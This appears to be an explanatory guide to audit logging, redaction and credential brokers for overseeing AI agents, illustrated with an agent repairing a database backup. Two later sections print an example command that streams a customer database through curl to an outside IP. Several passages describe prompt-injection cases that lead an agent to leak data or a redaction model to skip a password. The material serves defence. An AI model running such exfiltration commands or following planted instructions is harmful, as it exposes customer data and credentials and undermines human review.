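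Cooley also lists August 2030 as the deadline for high-risk systems that public authorities use. In the law, that date appears in the paragraph on systems already on the market before the main deadline, so a public authority that buys a new system shouldn't count on having until 2030.

Dana's backup agent probably isn't a high-risk system, so the six-month minimum may never apply to its logs. An agent that sorts job applications would be more likely to count as high-risk.

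*Article 12* of the EU AI Act (artificialintelligenceact.eu) requires high-risk systems to log events that help people identify risks and monitor the system. It lists minimum log contents only for certain biometric systems, and these include the people who checked each result. Some systems will need to log part of their inputs to make risks visible, but Article 12 doesn't require every company to save complete prompts and command output.

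Logs must be kept for at least six months unless other law, in particular data protection law, provides otherwise, according to both Mishcon de Reya's *Article 19 Automatically Generated Logs* and the European Commission's *Article 26*. Financial institutions must keep the logs with the records that financial law already requires, which may mean keeping them longer.

datenschutz notizen's *AI Logging Under the EU AI Act* argues that the minimum will help companies to justify keeping personal data, because the GDPR's "necessary" is hard to turn into a number of months. This is a reasonable argument, but a limited one. A company can't rely on a legal duty before it applies, and six months of required event logs don't justify three years of full traces. The same article suggests that logs of who reviewed a loan decision, and when, could show whether reviewers were approving everything automatically.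 That check needs names and times but not the applicants' bank statements.

The July amendment lets the EU's AI Office order a company to keep data that the office needs for supervision. According to Cooley, the office supervises systems whose maker also developed the underlying general-purpose model, with some exceptions. Courts can also order companies to preserve evidence. Software that deletes logs on a schedule therefore needs a way to pause deletion of particular records.

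### Why a log that nobody can alter is hard to clean

Article 12 doesn't require tamper-proof logs, but many companies want them. Without them, an administrator who approved a disastrous command could edit the entry afterwards, and so could an intruder or an agent with access to the log.

A common protection is a *hash chain*. A hash function, written H, turns any text into a short code of fixed length. Changing one character of the text gives a completely different code, and nobody knows a practical way to find two texts with the same code. For record number i, the log stores

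```
h_i = H(h_(i-1) || r_i)
```

Here `r_i` is the record, `h_(i-1)` is the code stored with the previous record, and `||` joins the two. The first record uses a fixed starting value. Each code therefore depends on every earlier record. If somebody changes record 5, its code no longer matches. Correcting that code breaks the match at record 6, and so on to the last record.

Someone with full control of the log could still change a record and recalculate all the later codes. To guard against this, the company regularly stores the newest code where the log's administrators can't change it, such as with an outside auditor. An auditor who holds the code for record 1,000 can then detect any change to the first 1,000 records. The chain doesn't show whether a record was true when the software wrote it.

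The same protection makes it hard to remove data logged by mistake. Suppose record 5 contains the password `fake-pw-41`. If Dana's company deletes it, the chain breaks, and an auditor can't distinguish the cleanup from a cover-up. The company could instead leave the record alone and change the password, but it can't do the same for personal data such as R. Osei's address.

Chaining only a hash of the content lets the company store the content separately and delete it, but the hash can still reveal text that is guessable. Someone who knows the form of Dana's command could hash it with one password after another and compare each result with the log. A modern graphics card can test billions of guesses per second, and a debt below 10,000.00 has only a million possible values.

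Encrypting the content before hashing it solves this problem. For each record, the software does the following:

1. It separates the record into a readable part, `m_i`, and restricted content, `x_i`.
2. It creates a random key, `k_i`, and encrypts the content: `c_i = E(k_i, x_i)`.
3. It hashes the encrypted content: `d_i = H(c_i)`.
4. It adds the record to the chain: `h_i = H(h_(i-1) || m_i || d_i)`.
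5. It puts `m_i`, `d_i` and `h_i` in the log, the encrypted content in a restricted store, and the key in a third place.

To erase the content, the company destroys `k_i`. The chain can still be verified, because it contains only the hash of the encrypted content. Nobody can test a guess at the content any longer without the random key. While the key exists, an auditor can hash the encrypted content, compare the result with the log and then decrypt the content. Some common encryption methods let a dishonest writer prepare encrypted content that decrypts to different messages under two keys, so a careful design also puts a hash of the key in the chain.

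The design also helps with backups. In the inventory for Dana's repair, nobody could delete the backup of the audit log before it expired after 90 days. Destroying the key immediately makes the encrypted content in every backup unreadable, as long as no copy of the key survives. If the company also keeps backups of its keys for 90 days, erasure still takes 90 days.

Destroying a key can't remove text that someone has already decrypted and pasted into a support ticket. A regulator might also object that the encrypted data still exists and that someone could break the encryption one day. The company should also delete the encrypted content wherever it can. Deleting it doesn't affect the chain.

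Encrypting each record with its own key lets a company erase single records, but it has to manage many keys. Using one key per day is simpler and suits a rule such as "erase everything after 30 days". But if a customer asks the company to delete their data, it would have to either destroy a whole day's content or re-encrypt the other records, which would then no longer match the chain.

### The backup record in two parts

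For Dana's backup, the part in the widely readable log might look like this, with shortened codes:

```
record      5127
time        2026-12-02 02:14:09
agent       backup-repair, session 883
action      shell: pg_dump
server      db.internal
account     backup
database    customers
output      /backups/nightly.sql
credential  backup-db-password (name only)
decision    allow, dana, after 41 seconds
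result      exit 0
content     9c41…e07a
chain       77f0…12bd
```

The restricted part, which only a few people may open, would contain the following before encryption:

```
record      5127
command     PGPASSWORD=[removed] pg_dump -h db.internal -U backup
            -f /backups/nightly.sql customers
evidence    backup.conf: host: db.internal
                         user: backup
                         password: fake-pw-41
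erase on    2027-01-01
```

In this example, a filter removed the password from the command but missed it in the configuration file. Encryption limits who can see the data that redaction misses, but redaction is still necessary.

The software should build the readable part from a fixed list of fields. Copying the whole command and then removing the sensitive parts would expose any missed password to the larger group of readers. If the software can't interpret a command, it should write "not interpreted" in the readable part and put the full text in the restricted one. Permitted fields can also leak information, because an output file's name can identify a customer just as a screenshot's filename can.

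The agent's check of the backup at 02:21 would get its own record, with the row count in the readable part and R. Osei's details only in the restricted part.

### What the company loses when it erases the content

After January 1, anyone reading the log can still see that Dana allowed the backup after 41 seconds and that it finished without an error. The auditor's copy of the chain can show that nobody has changed this record since. The exact command and the evidence behind it are gone, so nobody can fully judge whether Dana was right to allow the backup.

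Erasure also makes mistakes in the readable part permanent. If a command had two `-f` options and the logging software recorded only the first, which `pg_dump` ignores, the readable part would name the wrong file, and nobody could discover this from the log after the erasure.

Erasure can also make a later breach harder to handle. Cursor sent affected team administrators lists of the specific keys to rotate, which required knowing what was in the stolen traces. If an attacker copies a trace before the company erases it, the company may not know which secrets were exposed. Recording each credential's name in the readable part helps, but only for credentials the software recognized. Before erasing anything, the company should scan the content again and rotate any secrets it finds.

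An insider could also destroy a key to hide misconduct. Every erasure should therefore add a log entry with the time, the reason and the person responsible, and any erasure before the scheduled date should require a second person's approval.

The right retention period depends mainly on how soon people look for problems. If Dana's team reviews its agents' work every week, 30 days leaves time to investigate. If the only review is an annual audit, almost all the content will be gone by then, and the auditors will have to check approvals without seeing what Dana saw. The company could keep a small sample for longer, after removing customer data, or review its agents more often.

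## Redaction and what it misses

Deleting a trace after 30 days doesn't protect it from anyone who reads it before then. To hide sensitive values from those readers, companies use *redaction*, which means removing or replacing the values in a record before software shows or stores it. Software can easily replace a value it has found, but finding it is hard. In the two-part record of Dana's backup, the filter caught the password in the command but missed it in the configuration file.

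*Recall* is the share of real secrets that a detector finds, and *precision* is the share of the items it flags that are real secrets. Either figure alone can mislead about how well the detector works. For example, a filter that blanks out every line has perfect recall but leaves no text to read.

### Matching known formats

Most secret scanners look for known formats, as the scans of public code did, but each product has its own list. GitHub automatically masks 14 kinds of value in the logs of automated builds, including database connection strings, according to its *Secrets reference*. *NovaFabric* (2026), which describes a program that records agent sessions, lists connection strings among the values the program's scanner misses, along with passwords, login tokens and personal data. The address `postgres://backup:fake-pw-41@db.internal/customers` might therefore disappear from a GitHub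 build log but remain in a recorded agent session.

A scanner can also miss a key whose format is on its list. Mishra (2026), in *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, generated keys in known formats and put them in 12 contexts where keys appear in real code. Gitleaks found an Amazon key in `cfg = "AKIA..."` but not in `f(AKIA...)`. For six of the nine types of key it recognized, its patterns accepted only certain characters after the key, such as a quotation mark or a space, so it missed keys followed by a comma, a closing bracket or an ampersand. Keys in web addresses often come just before an ampersand, as in `?key=SECRET&next=1`. Mishra's own scanner missed any SendGrid key that ended in a hyphen, as about one in 64 do.

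TruffleHog had neither problem, but it reported an Amazon key ID only when the matching secret key was in the same file, and then it did so every time. Log software often processes one line at a time, so a pair of keys on separate lines might go undetected. Mishra tested particular versions of these tools, and later ones may behave differently.

Loose patterns cause the opposite problem: they remove harmless data. Another paper titled *NovaFabric* (2026) describes a September test of the same session recorder, in which its developers planted 14 kinds of key in each of ten synthetic records. The scanner removed all 140 keys, but it also destroyed a commit hash (the code that identifies one version of a project), a file checksum and a run ID in every record, because three patterns matched any string of the right length and characters. The developers narrowed the patterns, and the next test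 had no false alarms. However, the scanner no longer detects older keys from the database company Pinecone, because they have exactly the same form as run IDs and no pattern can tell them apart.

### Measuring randomness

Computer-generated keys look random, so a scanner can find keys in unfamiliar formats by measuring a string's *Shannon entropy*:

```
H = −Σ p_i · log2(p_i)
```

Here `p_i` is the share of the string's characters that are character i, and the sum covers every different character in the string. The result is in bits per character. It is 0 for `aaaa` and rises as a string uses more characters more evenly. In `fake-pw-41`, the hyphen makes up two of the ten characters, and each of the other eight appears once:

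```
H = 8 × 0.1 × log2(10) + 0.2 × log2(5) ≈ 3.12
```

| String | What it is | Entropy |
|---|---|---|
| `q7Zt2LmX9vRb4KcW7nHm` | A random key | 4.12 |
| `/backups/nightly.sql` | The backup's output path | 4.02 |
| `fake-pw-41` | The password | 3.12 |

*SecretSifter* (Gorijala, 2026) describes a scanner with a default threshold of 3.5. A scanner that used only that threshold would mask the output path, which Dana needs to see, and leave the password unmasked.

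Adjusting the entropy threshold doesn't fully solve this. A string of n characters can't have an entropy above log2(n), so no password shorter than 12 characters can reach 3.5. *Detecting Hard-Coded Credentials in Software Repositories via LLMs* (Biringa and Kul, 2025) defines passwords partly as short secrets with an entropy below 3.5. Lowering the threshold would catch more passwords, but also most ordinary words and filenames of a similar length. Scanners therefore combine entropy with other clues, such as the word `password` next to the value.

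### Matching a list of the company's own secrets

A filter that has a list of the company's secrets can find `fake-pw-41` anywhere, even in an ordinary sentence. GitHub does this in its build logs, where it replaces each secret that a team has registered with asterisks. GitHub's *Secure use reference* warns that automatic redaction isn't guaranteed and describes several gaps:

- GitHub mostly looks for the exact value. If a team stores a username and password together as one secret, in a format such as JSON, and a program prints only the password, the text no longer matches. Datadog has a rule that flags build scripts for this reason.
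- Encoding changes the value. In Base64, a common way of writing data as plain characters, `fake-pw-41` becomes `ZmFrZS1wdy00MQ==`.
- A program can use one secret to make another, such as a temporary login token signed with a private key. GitHub doesn't know the new value unless someone registers it.
- The machine that runs a job masks only the secrets that the job used.

The last gap matters most for agents, because they come across secrets that nobody gave them. Dana's agent found the password in a file on the server. A filter that checked only for secrets assigned to the agent would have missed it.

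GitHub advises teams to register encoded forms as well, but a password can be encoded together with many different strings. Some web services, for example, expect the username and password joined by a colon and encoded together in Base64. `backup:fake-pw-41` then becomes `YmFja3VwOmZha2UtcHctNDE=`, which doesn't contain the encoded form of the password alone. A more thorough filter decodes anything that looks encoded and searches the result. It should also allow for escaping, the extra characters that formats such as JSON insert before a quotation mark. Willison (2026) has released a redaction tool that does this.

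Exact matching works badly when a secret is an ordinary word. If the password were `backup`, the output path would read `/***s/nightly.sql`, and any reader could guess the missing word. The list of the company's secrets also needs strong protection, since it puts them all in one place.

### Recognizing names and personal details

Names and addresses have no fixed format, so software usually finds them with a trained model. *Model Card for OpenAI Privacy Filter* (de Bourcy, Ghalebikesabi and colleagues, 2026) describes one such model, which marks text in eight categories, including people, addresses, phone numbers and secrets. The model can run on a laptop, so a company can use it without sending its records to anyone.

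On PII-Masking-300k, a large set of synthetic texts in six languages, the model had 98.0% recall and 94.0% precision. It did much worse on short English examples with no description of the value, such as a phone number on its own. This table gives its recall:

| Category | Value alone | Description before the value | Description after the value |
|---|---|---|---|
| Person | 88.5% | 99.4% | 95.5% |
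| Phone number | 31.8% | 91.9% | 57.4% |
| Address | 21.4% | 41.4% | 36.8% |
| Secret | 36.1% | 70.8% | 41.6% |

Agent traces contain many values with no label beside them. In a database table, for example, the heading "Address" may appear once, above a thousand rows. Recall also fell as the distance between a value and the text explaining it grew, so the model could miss an address far down the table even if its input included the heading.

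For the line `R. Osei, 3 Mill Lane, overdue 212.40`, the ideal result would be `<PRIVATE_PERSON>, <PRIVATE_ADDRESS>, overdue 212.40`. The debt would stay because it isn't in any of the eight categories, and a user can't add a category without further training. That training can require little data. On a set of legal and medical questions, precision was 41% and recall 80% at first. Both rose to 96% after de Bourcy and colleagues trained the model on a tenth of the available examples.

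### Asking a language model to redact

A general language model can follow a written policy such as "remove anything about unpaid bills", so it isn't limited to fixed categories. Jeon, Kim and Shin (2026), in *RedacBench*, tested 11 models on 514 texts, mostly corporate and government emails. They broke the texts into 8,053 facts and checked which ones a reader could still infer after redaction.

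When the models masked words and phrases, they removed 36% to 52% of the sensitive facts and kept 73% to 85% of the harmless ones. Rewriting the text removed more. After two rounds of rewriting, GPT-5-mini had removed 80.9% of the sensitive facts but kept only 37.6% of the harmless ones. Current models may do better. The task was also harder than finding passwords, because the sensitive facts included business strategy.

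Rewriting is a poor choice for an audit log because an invented detail could mislead an investigation. When GPT-4.1 rewrote the texts, 3.36% of the statements in the result had no basis in the original. It is safer to have the model identify the sensitive passages and let ordinary software mask them.

Logs also arrive piece by piece, and a later entry can show that an earlier one was sensitive. When Jeon and colleagues gave GPT-4.1-nano each text in pieces, the share of sensitive facts it removed fell from 64.1% to 55.2%. The model also has access to the unredacted record, so it belongs in the inventory. An attacker could plant instructions in the record telling the model not to redact a password.

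### How accurate the detectors are

These are the main results from recent tests of secret detection:

| Test data | Detector | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| 198 values from one organization's web applications | SecretSifter | 86.8% | 79.8% |
| The same 198 values | TruffleHog | 89.9% | 35.9% |
| The same 198 values | SecretFinder | 4.3% | 31.8% |
| 400 generated keys of ten types | Gitleaks | 100% | 80–90% |
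| The same 400 keys | TruffleHog | 100% | 60% |
| CredData, an older collection of code with labeled secrets | Privacy Filter | 74.7% | 96.5% |
| 140 generated keys in agent records | NovaFabric, before its fix | 82.4% | 100% |

The figures depend heavily on the test data. TruffleHog's recall was 36% in one test and 60% in another, and Mishra declines to rank the tools because ten types of key are too few. Privacy Filter's CredData scores count pieces of text rather than whole secrets, so it gets partial credit for masking half a password.

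There is particular reason to be cautious about SecretSifter's lead. Gorijala built the scanner and knew what kinds of credentials this organization used. Of the 198 values, 37 were encrypted settings that only SecretSifter could decrypt, and another 40 were identifiers that aren't secrets on their own. When Gorijala added six rules to the competing scanners that accept custom rules, the best of them did about as well as SecretSifter on unencrypted text.

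Only the NovaFabric test used agent records. It was also the easiest test, because every planted key matched a format the scanner already had. An earlier version planted a made-up key in a different format, and the scanner missed it in all ten runs. None of these results gives a good estimate for Dana's log, where the main secret is a short password that somebody chose.

### What 90% recall means for a log

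Suppose that a company writes 10,000 log records a day and 1% of them contain a secret. Its detector has 90% recall and wrongly flags 2% of clean records. These figures are illustrative, but they show what happens when secrets are rare:

| | Masked | Not masked | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Records with a secret | 90 | 10 | 100 |
| Clean records | 198 | 9,702 | 9,900 |

The detector misses 10 secrets a day and wrongly masks 198 clean records. Its precision is 90 ÷ (90 + 198), or 31%, so more than two-thirds of the masked records contained no secrets.

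Precision is this low because clean records outnumber those with secrets by 99 to 1. If 10% of records contained a secret, the same detector would correctly mask 900 of them and wrongly mask 180 clean ones, for a precision of 83%. A precision figure from a test set with many secrets therefore doesn't apply to an ordinary log. In Mishra's main comparison, 400 of the 1,100 samples were secrets.

The 10 missed secrets also probably cluster by type. In the same comparison, each scanner found either every key of a given type or none. If the detector misses the type of password Dana uses, it will miss hers every night, and after a month the log will contain at least 30 copies. A list of the types a detector misses is therefore more useful to the company than the detector's average recall.

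### What most detectors miss

*Passwords with no format.* Neither of Apiiro's two scanners flagged 215 of the files it had found, mainly because of passwords in commands. A filter can mask whatever follows `PGPASSWORD=`, `sshpass -p` or `mysql -p` (Cornelißen's examples), but a password in an ordinary sentence has no such marker. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) points out that detectors built for code don't cover secrets in an agent's plain-language instructions or in printed output. Only checking the text against a list of known secrets will find these reliably.

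Redaction can miss values that are split into pieces. People sometimes add spaces to a key, and log software may cut a long message in two. When de Bourcy and colleagues put unusual spaces into values, Privacy Filter's recall was 63.1%. With line breaks, recall was 81.2%, but precision fell to 45.3% because the model wrongly labeled fragments of web addresses as people's names. Software that receives an agent's output a few words at a time should join the pieces before searching them.

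*Images.* A trace often stores a screenshot as Base64 text, which can run to hundreds of thousands of random-looking characters. An entropy-based filter may mask the whole picture, while one that skips very long strings will leave it untouched. Neither checks what the picture shows, so the safest approach is to keep images out of the text log and handle them separately. A solid box is better than blurring for hiding part of an image, because an attacker can blur many guesses in the same way and see which one matches.

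Redaction can miss facts that identify someone only in combination. A time, a branch and an amount may each look harmless, but together they can identify a person. After redaction, R. Osei's line still contains a debt of 212.40, and anyone who can open the billing page can search for that amount and may find exactly one customer. Detectors that examine one value at a time can't catch this. The tests by Jeon and colleagues come closer, because they count a fact as removed only if nobody could infer it from the remaining text.

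### What to put in a value's place

Once software has found a value, it has to put something in the log instead. The main options differ in what they let readers do:

| Replacement | Example | Can readers see that two values match? | Who can recover the value? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blank | `***` | No | Nobody |
| Typed label | `[PASSWORD]` | No | Nobody |
| Reversible token | `tok_58213` | Yes | Anyone with access to the lookup table |
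| Plain hash | `b7e2…19ac` | Yes | Anyone who can guess the value |
| Keyed fingerprint | `fp_3e91c07a52d4` | Yes | Someone who has the key and can guess the value |

A blank reveals the least, but a reader can't tell whether it replaced a password, a customer's name or a file path. A typed label shows which it was and reveals little more. *When Only the Final Text Survives* (2026) replaced names and emails with labels such as `[NAME]`, and its software could still trace which agent had written what almost as well as before. People may find it harder, because "`[NAME]` asked to cancel `[NAME]`'s debt" could describe one person or two. Numbered labels such as `[NAME 1]` and `[NAME 2]` remove that ambiguity within a single record.

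A reversible token is a random code that a separate table links to the original value. Reversible tokens suit customer data, since an investigator may later need to know who the customer was. They make little sense for passwords, because nobody investigating an incident needs to know Dana's password, and the table would be one more place to steal it from.

A plain hash lets readers match values across logs, but, as with a hash chain, anyone who copies the log can test guesses against the hash. There are 26^8, or about 2.1 × 10^11, possible passwords of eight lowercase letters. At 10^10 guesses a second, trying them all takes about 21 seconds. A deliberately slow hash function that allowed only 10,000 guesses a second would stretch this to about eight months, but an attacker would try common passwords first and might succeed within minutes.

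A *keyed fingerprint* closes this gap by mixing a private key into the calculation:

```
F = first 12 characters of HMAC(k, v)
```

HMAC is a standard method for computing a code, here used as a fingerprint, from a key and a value. Someone who has the log but not the key can't test guesses at the password. Before changing the password, Dana could use its fingerprint to find every program that used it. The next night, a new fingerprint would confirm that the backup had switched to the new password.

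Twelve hexadecimal characters give about 2.8 × 10^14 possible fingerprints. Among 10,000 different secrets, the chance that any two share a fingerprint is less than one in a million. With eight characters, it would be about 1%, enough to cause an occasional false match.

The key has to stay out of reach of the people who read the logs. They also shouldn't have access to any service that fingerprints whatever they type, because they could use it to test guesses. Fingerprints of customer names also let a reader follow one customer through thousands of entries, a few of which may reveal who the customer is. Using a different key for each log limits this, but then nobody can match values between logs.

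### Redacting at capture, in transit or at display

Redaction protects only the copies that software makes after it. The later it happens, the more unprotected copies remain:

| Stage | What happens | What still contains the secret |
|---|---|---|
| Capture | The agent's software redacts a record before writing it | The original file, the program's memory and any prompts already sent to the model |
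| Transit | A separate program redacts records on their way to the log store | All of the above, plus local log files, error files and queues of unsent records |
| Display | The dashboard masks values when someone opens a record | All of the above, plus the log store, its backups, its search index and exports |

Another advantage of redacting at capture is that the password is still in its own named field. In *Secrets in Logs*, the developer nchika (2026) tested a filter that removes fields by name. It removed a wallet's recovery phrase when the program logged the phrase as a separate field, but missed it when the program first joined all the fields into one piece of text. nchika recommends logging only fields that someone has approved as safe, because a list of forbidden fields won't cover new ones. But redacting at capture requires a separate filter for every program, and nobody can recover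 what a filter removes by mistake.

Redacting in transit lets a security team update one set of rules for every program, including those whose code it can't change. But by then many values are already part of longer text, so detecting them is less reliable.

Masking a secret only on screen keeps the original available for investigations. In the terminal program Warp, users can hover over a masked secret to reveal or copy it, which is convenient on their own computer. If they turn on redaction before sharing the output through a link, Warp removes the secret from the shared copy. Oversight records also need to distinguish between hiding a secret and removing it, because a dashboard that only hides a password may still send it to the reader's browser.

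These stages work best together. A company could remove known secrets at capture, scan for unknown ones in transit, and reserve masking at display for personal details that some readers are allowed to see. *NovaFabric* scans each record again after redacting it. A second scan that uses the same rules will catch processing errors but miss the same secrets as the first, so a different detector is a better choice.

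Redaction also can't stop someone who wants to get around it. CloudBees' *Mask ephemeral secrets in Pipeline build logs* calls masking "a secondary, best-effort defense", because the author of a build script can easily bypass it. An agent could do the same by printing a password backwards. A credential broker avoids the problem by keeping the password away from the agent.

### When redaction hides the harm

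The strongest argument against heavy redaction is that it can remove the very detail that makes an action dangerous. Suppose that an attacker tricks Dana's agent into proposing this command:

`pg_dump -h db.internal -U backup customers | curl -T - https://203.0.113.9/in`

The command sends the whole customer database to an unknown server. Warp's default list of values to mask includes IP addresses, and Privacy Filter has a category for private web addresses. Either could replace the destination with a blank or a label, and the command might then look like an ordinary backup to another company server. An attacker who knows the filter's rules could also hide a harmful instruction, for example by putting it after `password=`.

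Over-redaction also harms later investigations. If a filter removes a commit hash, as *NovaFabric* did before its fix, nobody can tell which version of the code the agent installed. Engineers who keep finding blanked-out records may turn the filter off.

These are good reasons to redact precisely, but they don't justify leaving passwords in. The filter should keep the details Dana uses to judge a command, such as the server and the destination, unless they contain a secret. It should also parse each command first and mask only fixed values, never anything the shell would run.

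A company can also run automated checks on the original command before redacting it. A check could block any upload to an unfamiliar address and record only the result. If the check runs on the company's own machines, no outside provider sees the secrets in the command. For cases that the checks miss, the company can keep an encrypted copy of the original so that a few investigators can see what the filter removed.

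Some evidence suggests that redacted traces can stay useful. *RedAct* (2026) describes a method for removing a company's know-how from agent traces. The redacted traces kept 91.0% to 96.6% of the final answers, tool names and other evidence that auditors need. But they also kept 29.4% of the material the method was supposed to remove, which would be far too much if that material were passwords.

Personal details are harder to redact because the reviewer sometimes needs the value that the filter removed. Every mask should therefore show what kind of value it replaced and which rule applied. If the destination is masked, the reviewer can then ask to see it, and should refuse approval if nobody can provide it.

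## Showing reviewers enough to decide without showing the secret

A filter that edits a finished command can remove a detail the reviewer needs, because its rules are based on the values in the command, not on what the reviewer has to decide. It is safer to list what the reviewer must know to make the decision and build the request from that list.

Six items cover most agent actions. The table shows them for Dana's backup and for an agent's proposed email to R. Osei about an unpaid bill.

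| What the reviewer must know | Backup repair | Email to a customer |
|---|---|---|
| Action | Copy a database to a file | Send one email |
| Target | `customers` on `db.internal`, a production server | The company's billing mailbox |
| Data leaving the company | None | Name, debt and the text of the email |
| Recipient | The folder `/backups` | R. Osei's email address |
| Reversibility | Replaces a file | Nobody can take it back |
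| Reason | The nightly backup failed | The bill is 30 days overdue |
| Raw values needed | Server, account and path | Address, amount and full text |

Dana can judge the backup without seeing the password or any customer records, but the reviewer has to read the email to check that the agent picked the right person and amount.

Showing reviewers the raw values in bulk data exposes a lot and helps them very little, because nobody reads 12,400 customer rows before approving an export. The number of rows, the column names and the filter that selected the rows are more useful, perhaps with two invented rows to show the format.

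Occasionally a decision does depend on a secret. An agent might want to publish a file containing a string that could be a real key or a placeholder. Even then, software can compare the string with the company's stored secrets and report "matches a live key". Reviewers can also use keyed fingerprints to check whether two programs use the same password.

### The study of consequence-oriented approval

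Leaving out details is safe only if the reviewer can decide without them. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (November 2026), Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues tested how much different details help the reviewer decide.

They start with a leak that a reviewer can't catch from an ordinary approval request. A user asks an agent to check supplier invoices and send an outside auditor "summary totals only". Hidden instructions in one supplier's note lead the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`. The agent then asks to send the file to the auditor. The request looks fine because the auditor is an approved recipient and the filename is ordinary. Sending the file would break the user's rule only because of the raw rows the agent put in it several steps earlier.

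The researchers built an interface that shows the reviewer four things:

- the user's original restriction, word for word
- the exact tool, file and recipient
- one sentence on the combined effect of this action and the earlier ones
- the recorded events behind that sentence, which the reviewer can open

In the invoice case, the reviewer learns from the sentence that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor. The sentence doesn't include a judgment that this is a violation, so the reviewer still has to compare these facts with the restriction. The facts come from software that records the agent's actions and tracks which files the agent made from which others, not from the agent's own account.

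Eighty unpaid volunteers, recruited through social media, each used one of four interfaces to make 12 decisions. Half of the requests were malicious.

| Interface | What it showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Conventional prompt | A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments | Also the exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
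| Chronological log | Also the restriction and every earlier event | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| Consequence view | The same facts as the log, organized around the effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. Organizing it better seems to have helped too, but the evidence is weak. After statistical adjustment, people using the consequence view approved unsafe requests 7.9 percentage points less often than people using the log, with a 95% interval from 19.7 points less often to 3.8 points more often. When the violation depended on a chain of several steps, each group approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests. Real reviewers also see far fewer attacks than these volunteers did, and may be less alert.

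The results are a warning against cutting approval requests down to a line or two, but they don't show that reviewers need to see secrets. The sentence about the invoices explains where the data came from without displaying any rows. Hossain and colleagues didn't compare masked requests with unmasked ones, so it is still only a reasonable assumption that hiding a password doesn't affect the decision.

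### What people look at and what they ask for

People who use agents at work judge requests on much the same items as the list above. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 more, of whom 107 answered the questions about permissions. Of those 107, 76.6% said they look harder at requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges, and 67.3% said they were less likely to approve an action that didn't fit the task. The researchers also found that people consider whether they could undo an action, and they recommend that requests say whether and how it can be undone.

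When asked what they would like to see, 57.9% of respondents chose a lasting log of the agent's activity and 45.8% chose a clearer view of what it had accessed. A list of opened files would provide that view without revealing their contents. A lasting log is harder to provide safely because it can leak data in the same ways as an audit log.

Only 47.7% of people said they carefully read the approval requests they already get, while about a third said they skim them and a fifth said they approve by default. These figures are self-reported, so the true ones are probably worse. Dhanorkar and colleagues found that developers also take shortcuts when they review finished work, such as checking the agent's plan and assuming the agent followed it. An approval request should take its facts from the actual command, because a plan that was accurate when the agent wrote it can be wrong by the time it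 acts.

Showing reviewers the full command can expose a password and still leave them unsure what the command does. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of agents damaging files. In 31 of them, the approval prompt showed a command whose effect the user couldn't work out. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine but runs whatever is in the script. In 80 reports, including some of those 31, the user had approved everything in advance, often to avoid hundreds of prompts per session.

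### Keeping the secret in a credential broker

A credential broker keeps the password out of the agent's session, so the oversight channels have no password to copy. Many brokers are proxies for web requests. Docker's *Credentials* describes one for agents that run in a sandbox, a closed-off environment on a computer. The agent sends its request with a dummy value, which a proxy outside the sandbox replaces with the real credential before forwarding the request. Anthropic uses a proxy that fetches credentials from a separate store, so the software around the agent never handles them. InfoQ (2026) reports that GitHub's agent workflows also send API tokens through proxies outside the agent's container. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) explains that everything in one of its automated jobs shares the same level of trust by default, so a misbehaving agent could reach the login secrets.

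A proxy that fills in web headers wouldn't help Dana, because a PostgreSQL login doesn't use them. Her company needs a broker that runs the backup itself. Jin, Guo and Cheung (2026), in *CapSeal*, describe a broker that runs commands on remote servers in this way. A similar one for databases could work as follows:

1. An administrator stores the password under the name `backup-db-password` and allows its use only for the account `backup` on `db.internal`.
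2. The agent asks the broker to copy `customers` to `/backups/nightly.sql` with that credential.
3. The broker checks the request against its rules and, if they require it, waits for Dana's approval.
4. The broker runs `pg_dump` with the password, removes any credentials from the output and returns the rest to the agent.
5. The broker logs the action with the credential's name.

Some evidence suggests that brokers keep secrets hidden. Jin and colleagues prompted agents to reveal an API key. The two systems that gave the agent the key leaked it in every trial, and the broker never did. The broker's result is almost guaranteed by design, since an agent can't reveal a key it never received. The tests are weaker evidence that the broker prevents misuse, because none of the systems, including the two without a broker, allowed unauthorized use of a credential.

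*API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* reports Corvic AI's September 2026 test of its own broker. Test code running in the agent's environment searched settings and files for the credential and sent requests to websites that return whatever they receive. The credential never appeared, and all 16 checks passed. The test didn't cover redirects to other sites or cases where an attacker controls a service the broker trusts.

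A broker takes work to set up. One of Corvic's connections failed because the broker put the key in a header, while the service expected it in the web address. The company also has to remove the old copies of its credentials. *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a broker for agents in healthcare, mentions an audit that found credentials scattered across shell settings and configuration files, some readable by every user on the machine. If `fake-pw-41` stays in the backup script's configuration file, Dana's agent may find it there again.

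Hiding a credential also doesn't limit what it can do. *Your engineers are handing private keys to AI agents* (Dodds, 2026) recounts an April 2026 accident at PocketOS, a car rental software company. A Cursor agent ran into a login problem in a test environment and decided to delete a storage volume. It found a token in an unrelated file and used it, and nine seconds later the company's production data was gone. The hosting company later restored the data from its own backups. The token was for managing web domains, but it allowed any operation. A broker would have kept the token out of the file, but if the broker's rules had also allowed any operation, the agent could have deleted the volume without ever seeing the token. Dodds, who sells a broker, acknowledges this limit. The Corvic researchers rate over-broad access as the threat their broker reduces least, from 20 to 15 out of 25, though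 these scores are their own judgments.

A broker doesn't protect customer data at all, so the customer rows would still be in the trace of Dana's repair.

### Facts computed by trusted software

The previous section gave an example in which an attacker tricks Dana's agent into sending the customer database to an unknown server:

`pg_dump -h db.internal -U backup customers | curl -T - https://203.0.113.9/in`

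A tired reviewer could easily take this for a backup. The line "production database, 12,400 customer rows, new recipient" is much harder to misread, and it contains no customer data. The agent shouldn't write that line, because an agent that has followed an attacker's instructions may describe the command as a backup too. Separate software can produce it in five steps:

1. Split the command into programs, options and values without running it.
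2. Look up each server and folder in a list that the company maintains, which records `db.internal` as production.
3. Measure what the action would affect, for example by counting the rows or checking whether the output file already exists.
4. Compare the recipient with those in earlier approved requests.
5. Write the results into fixed fields, and write "unknown" wherever a step failed.

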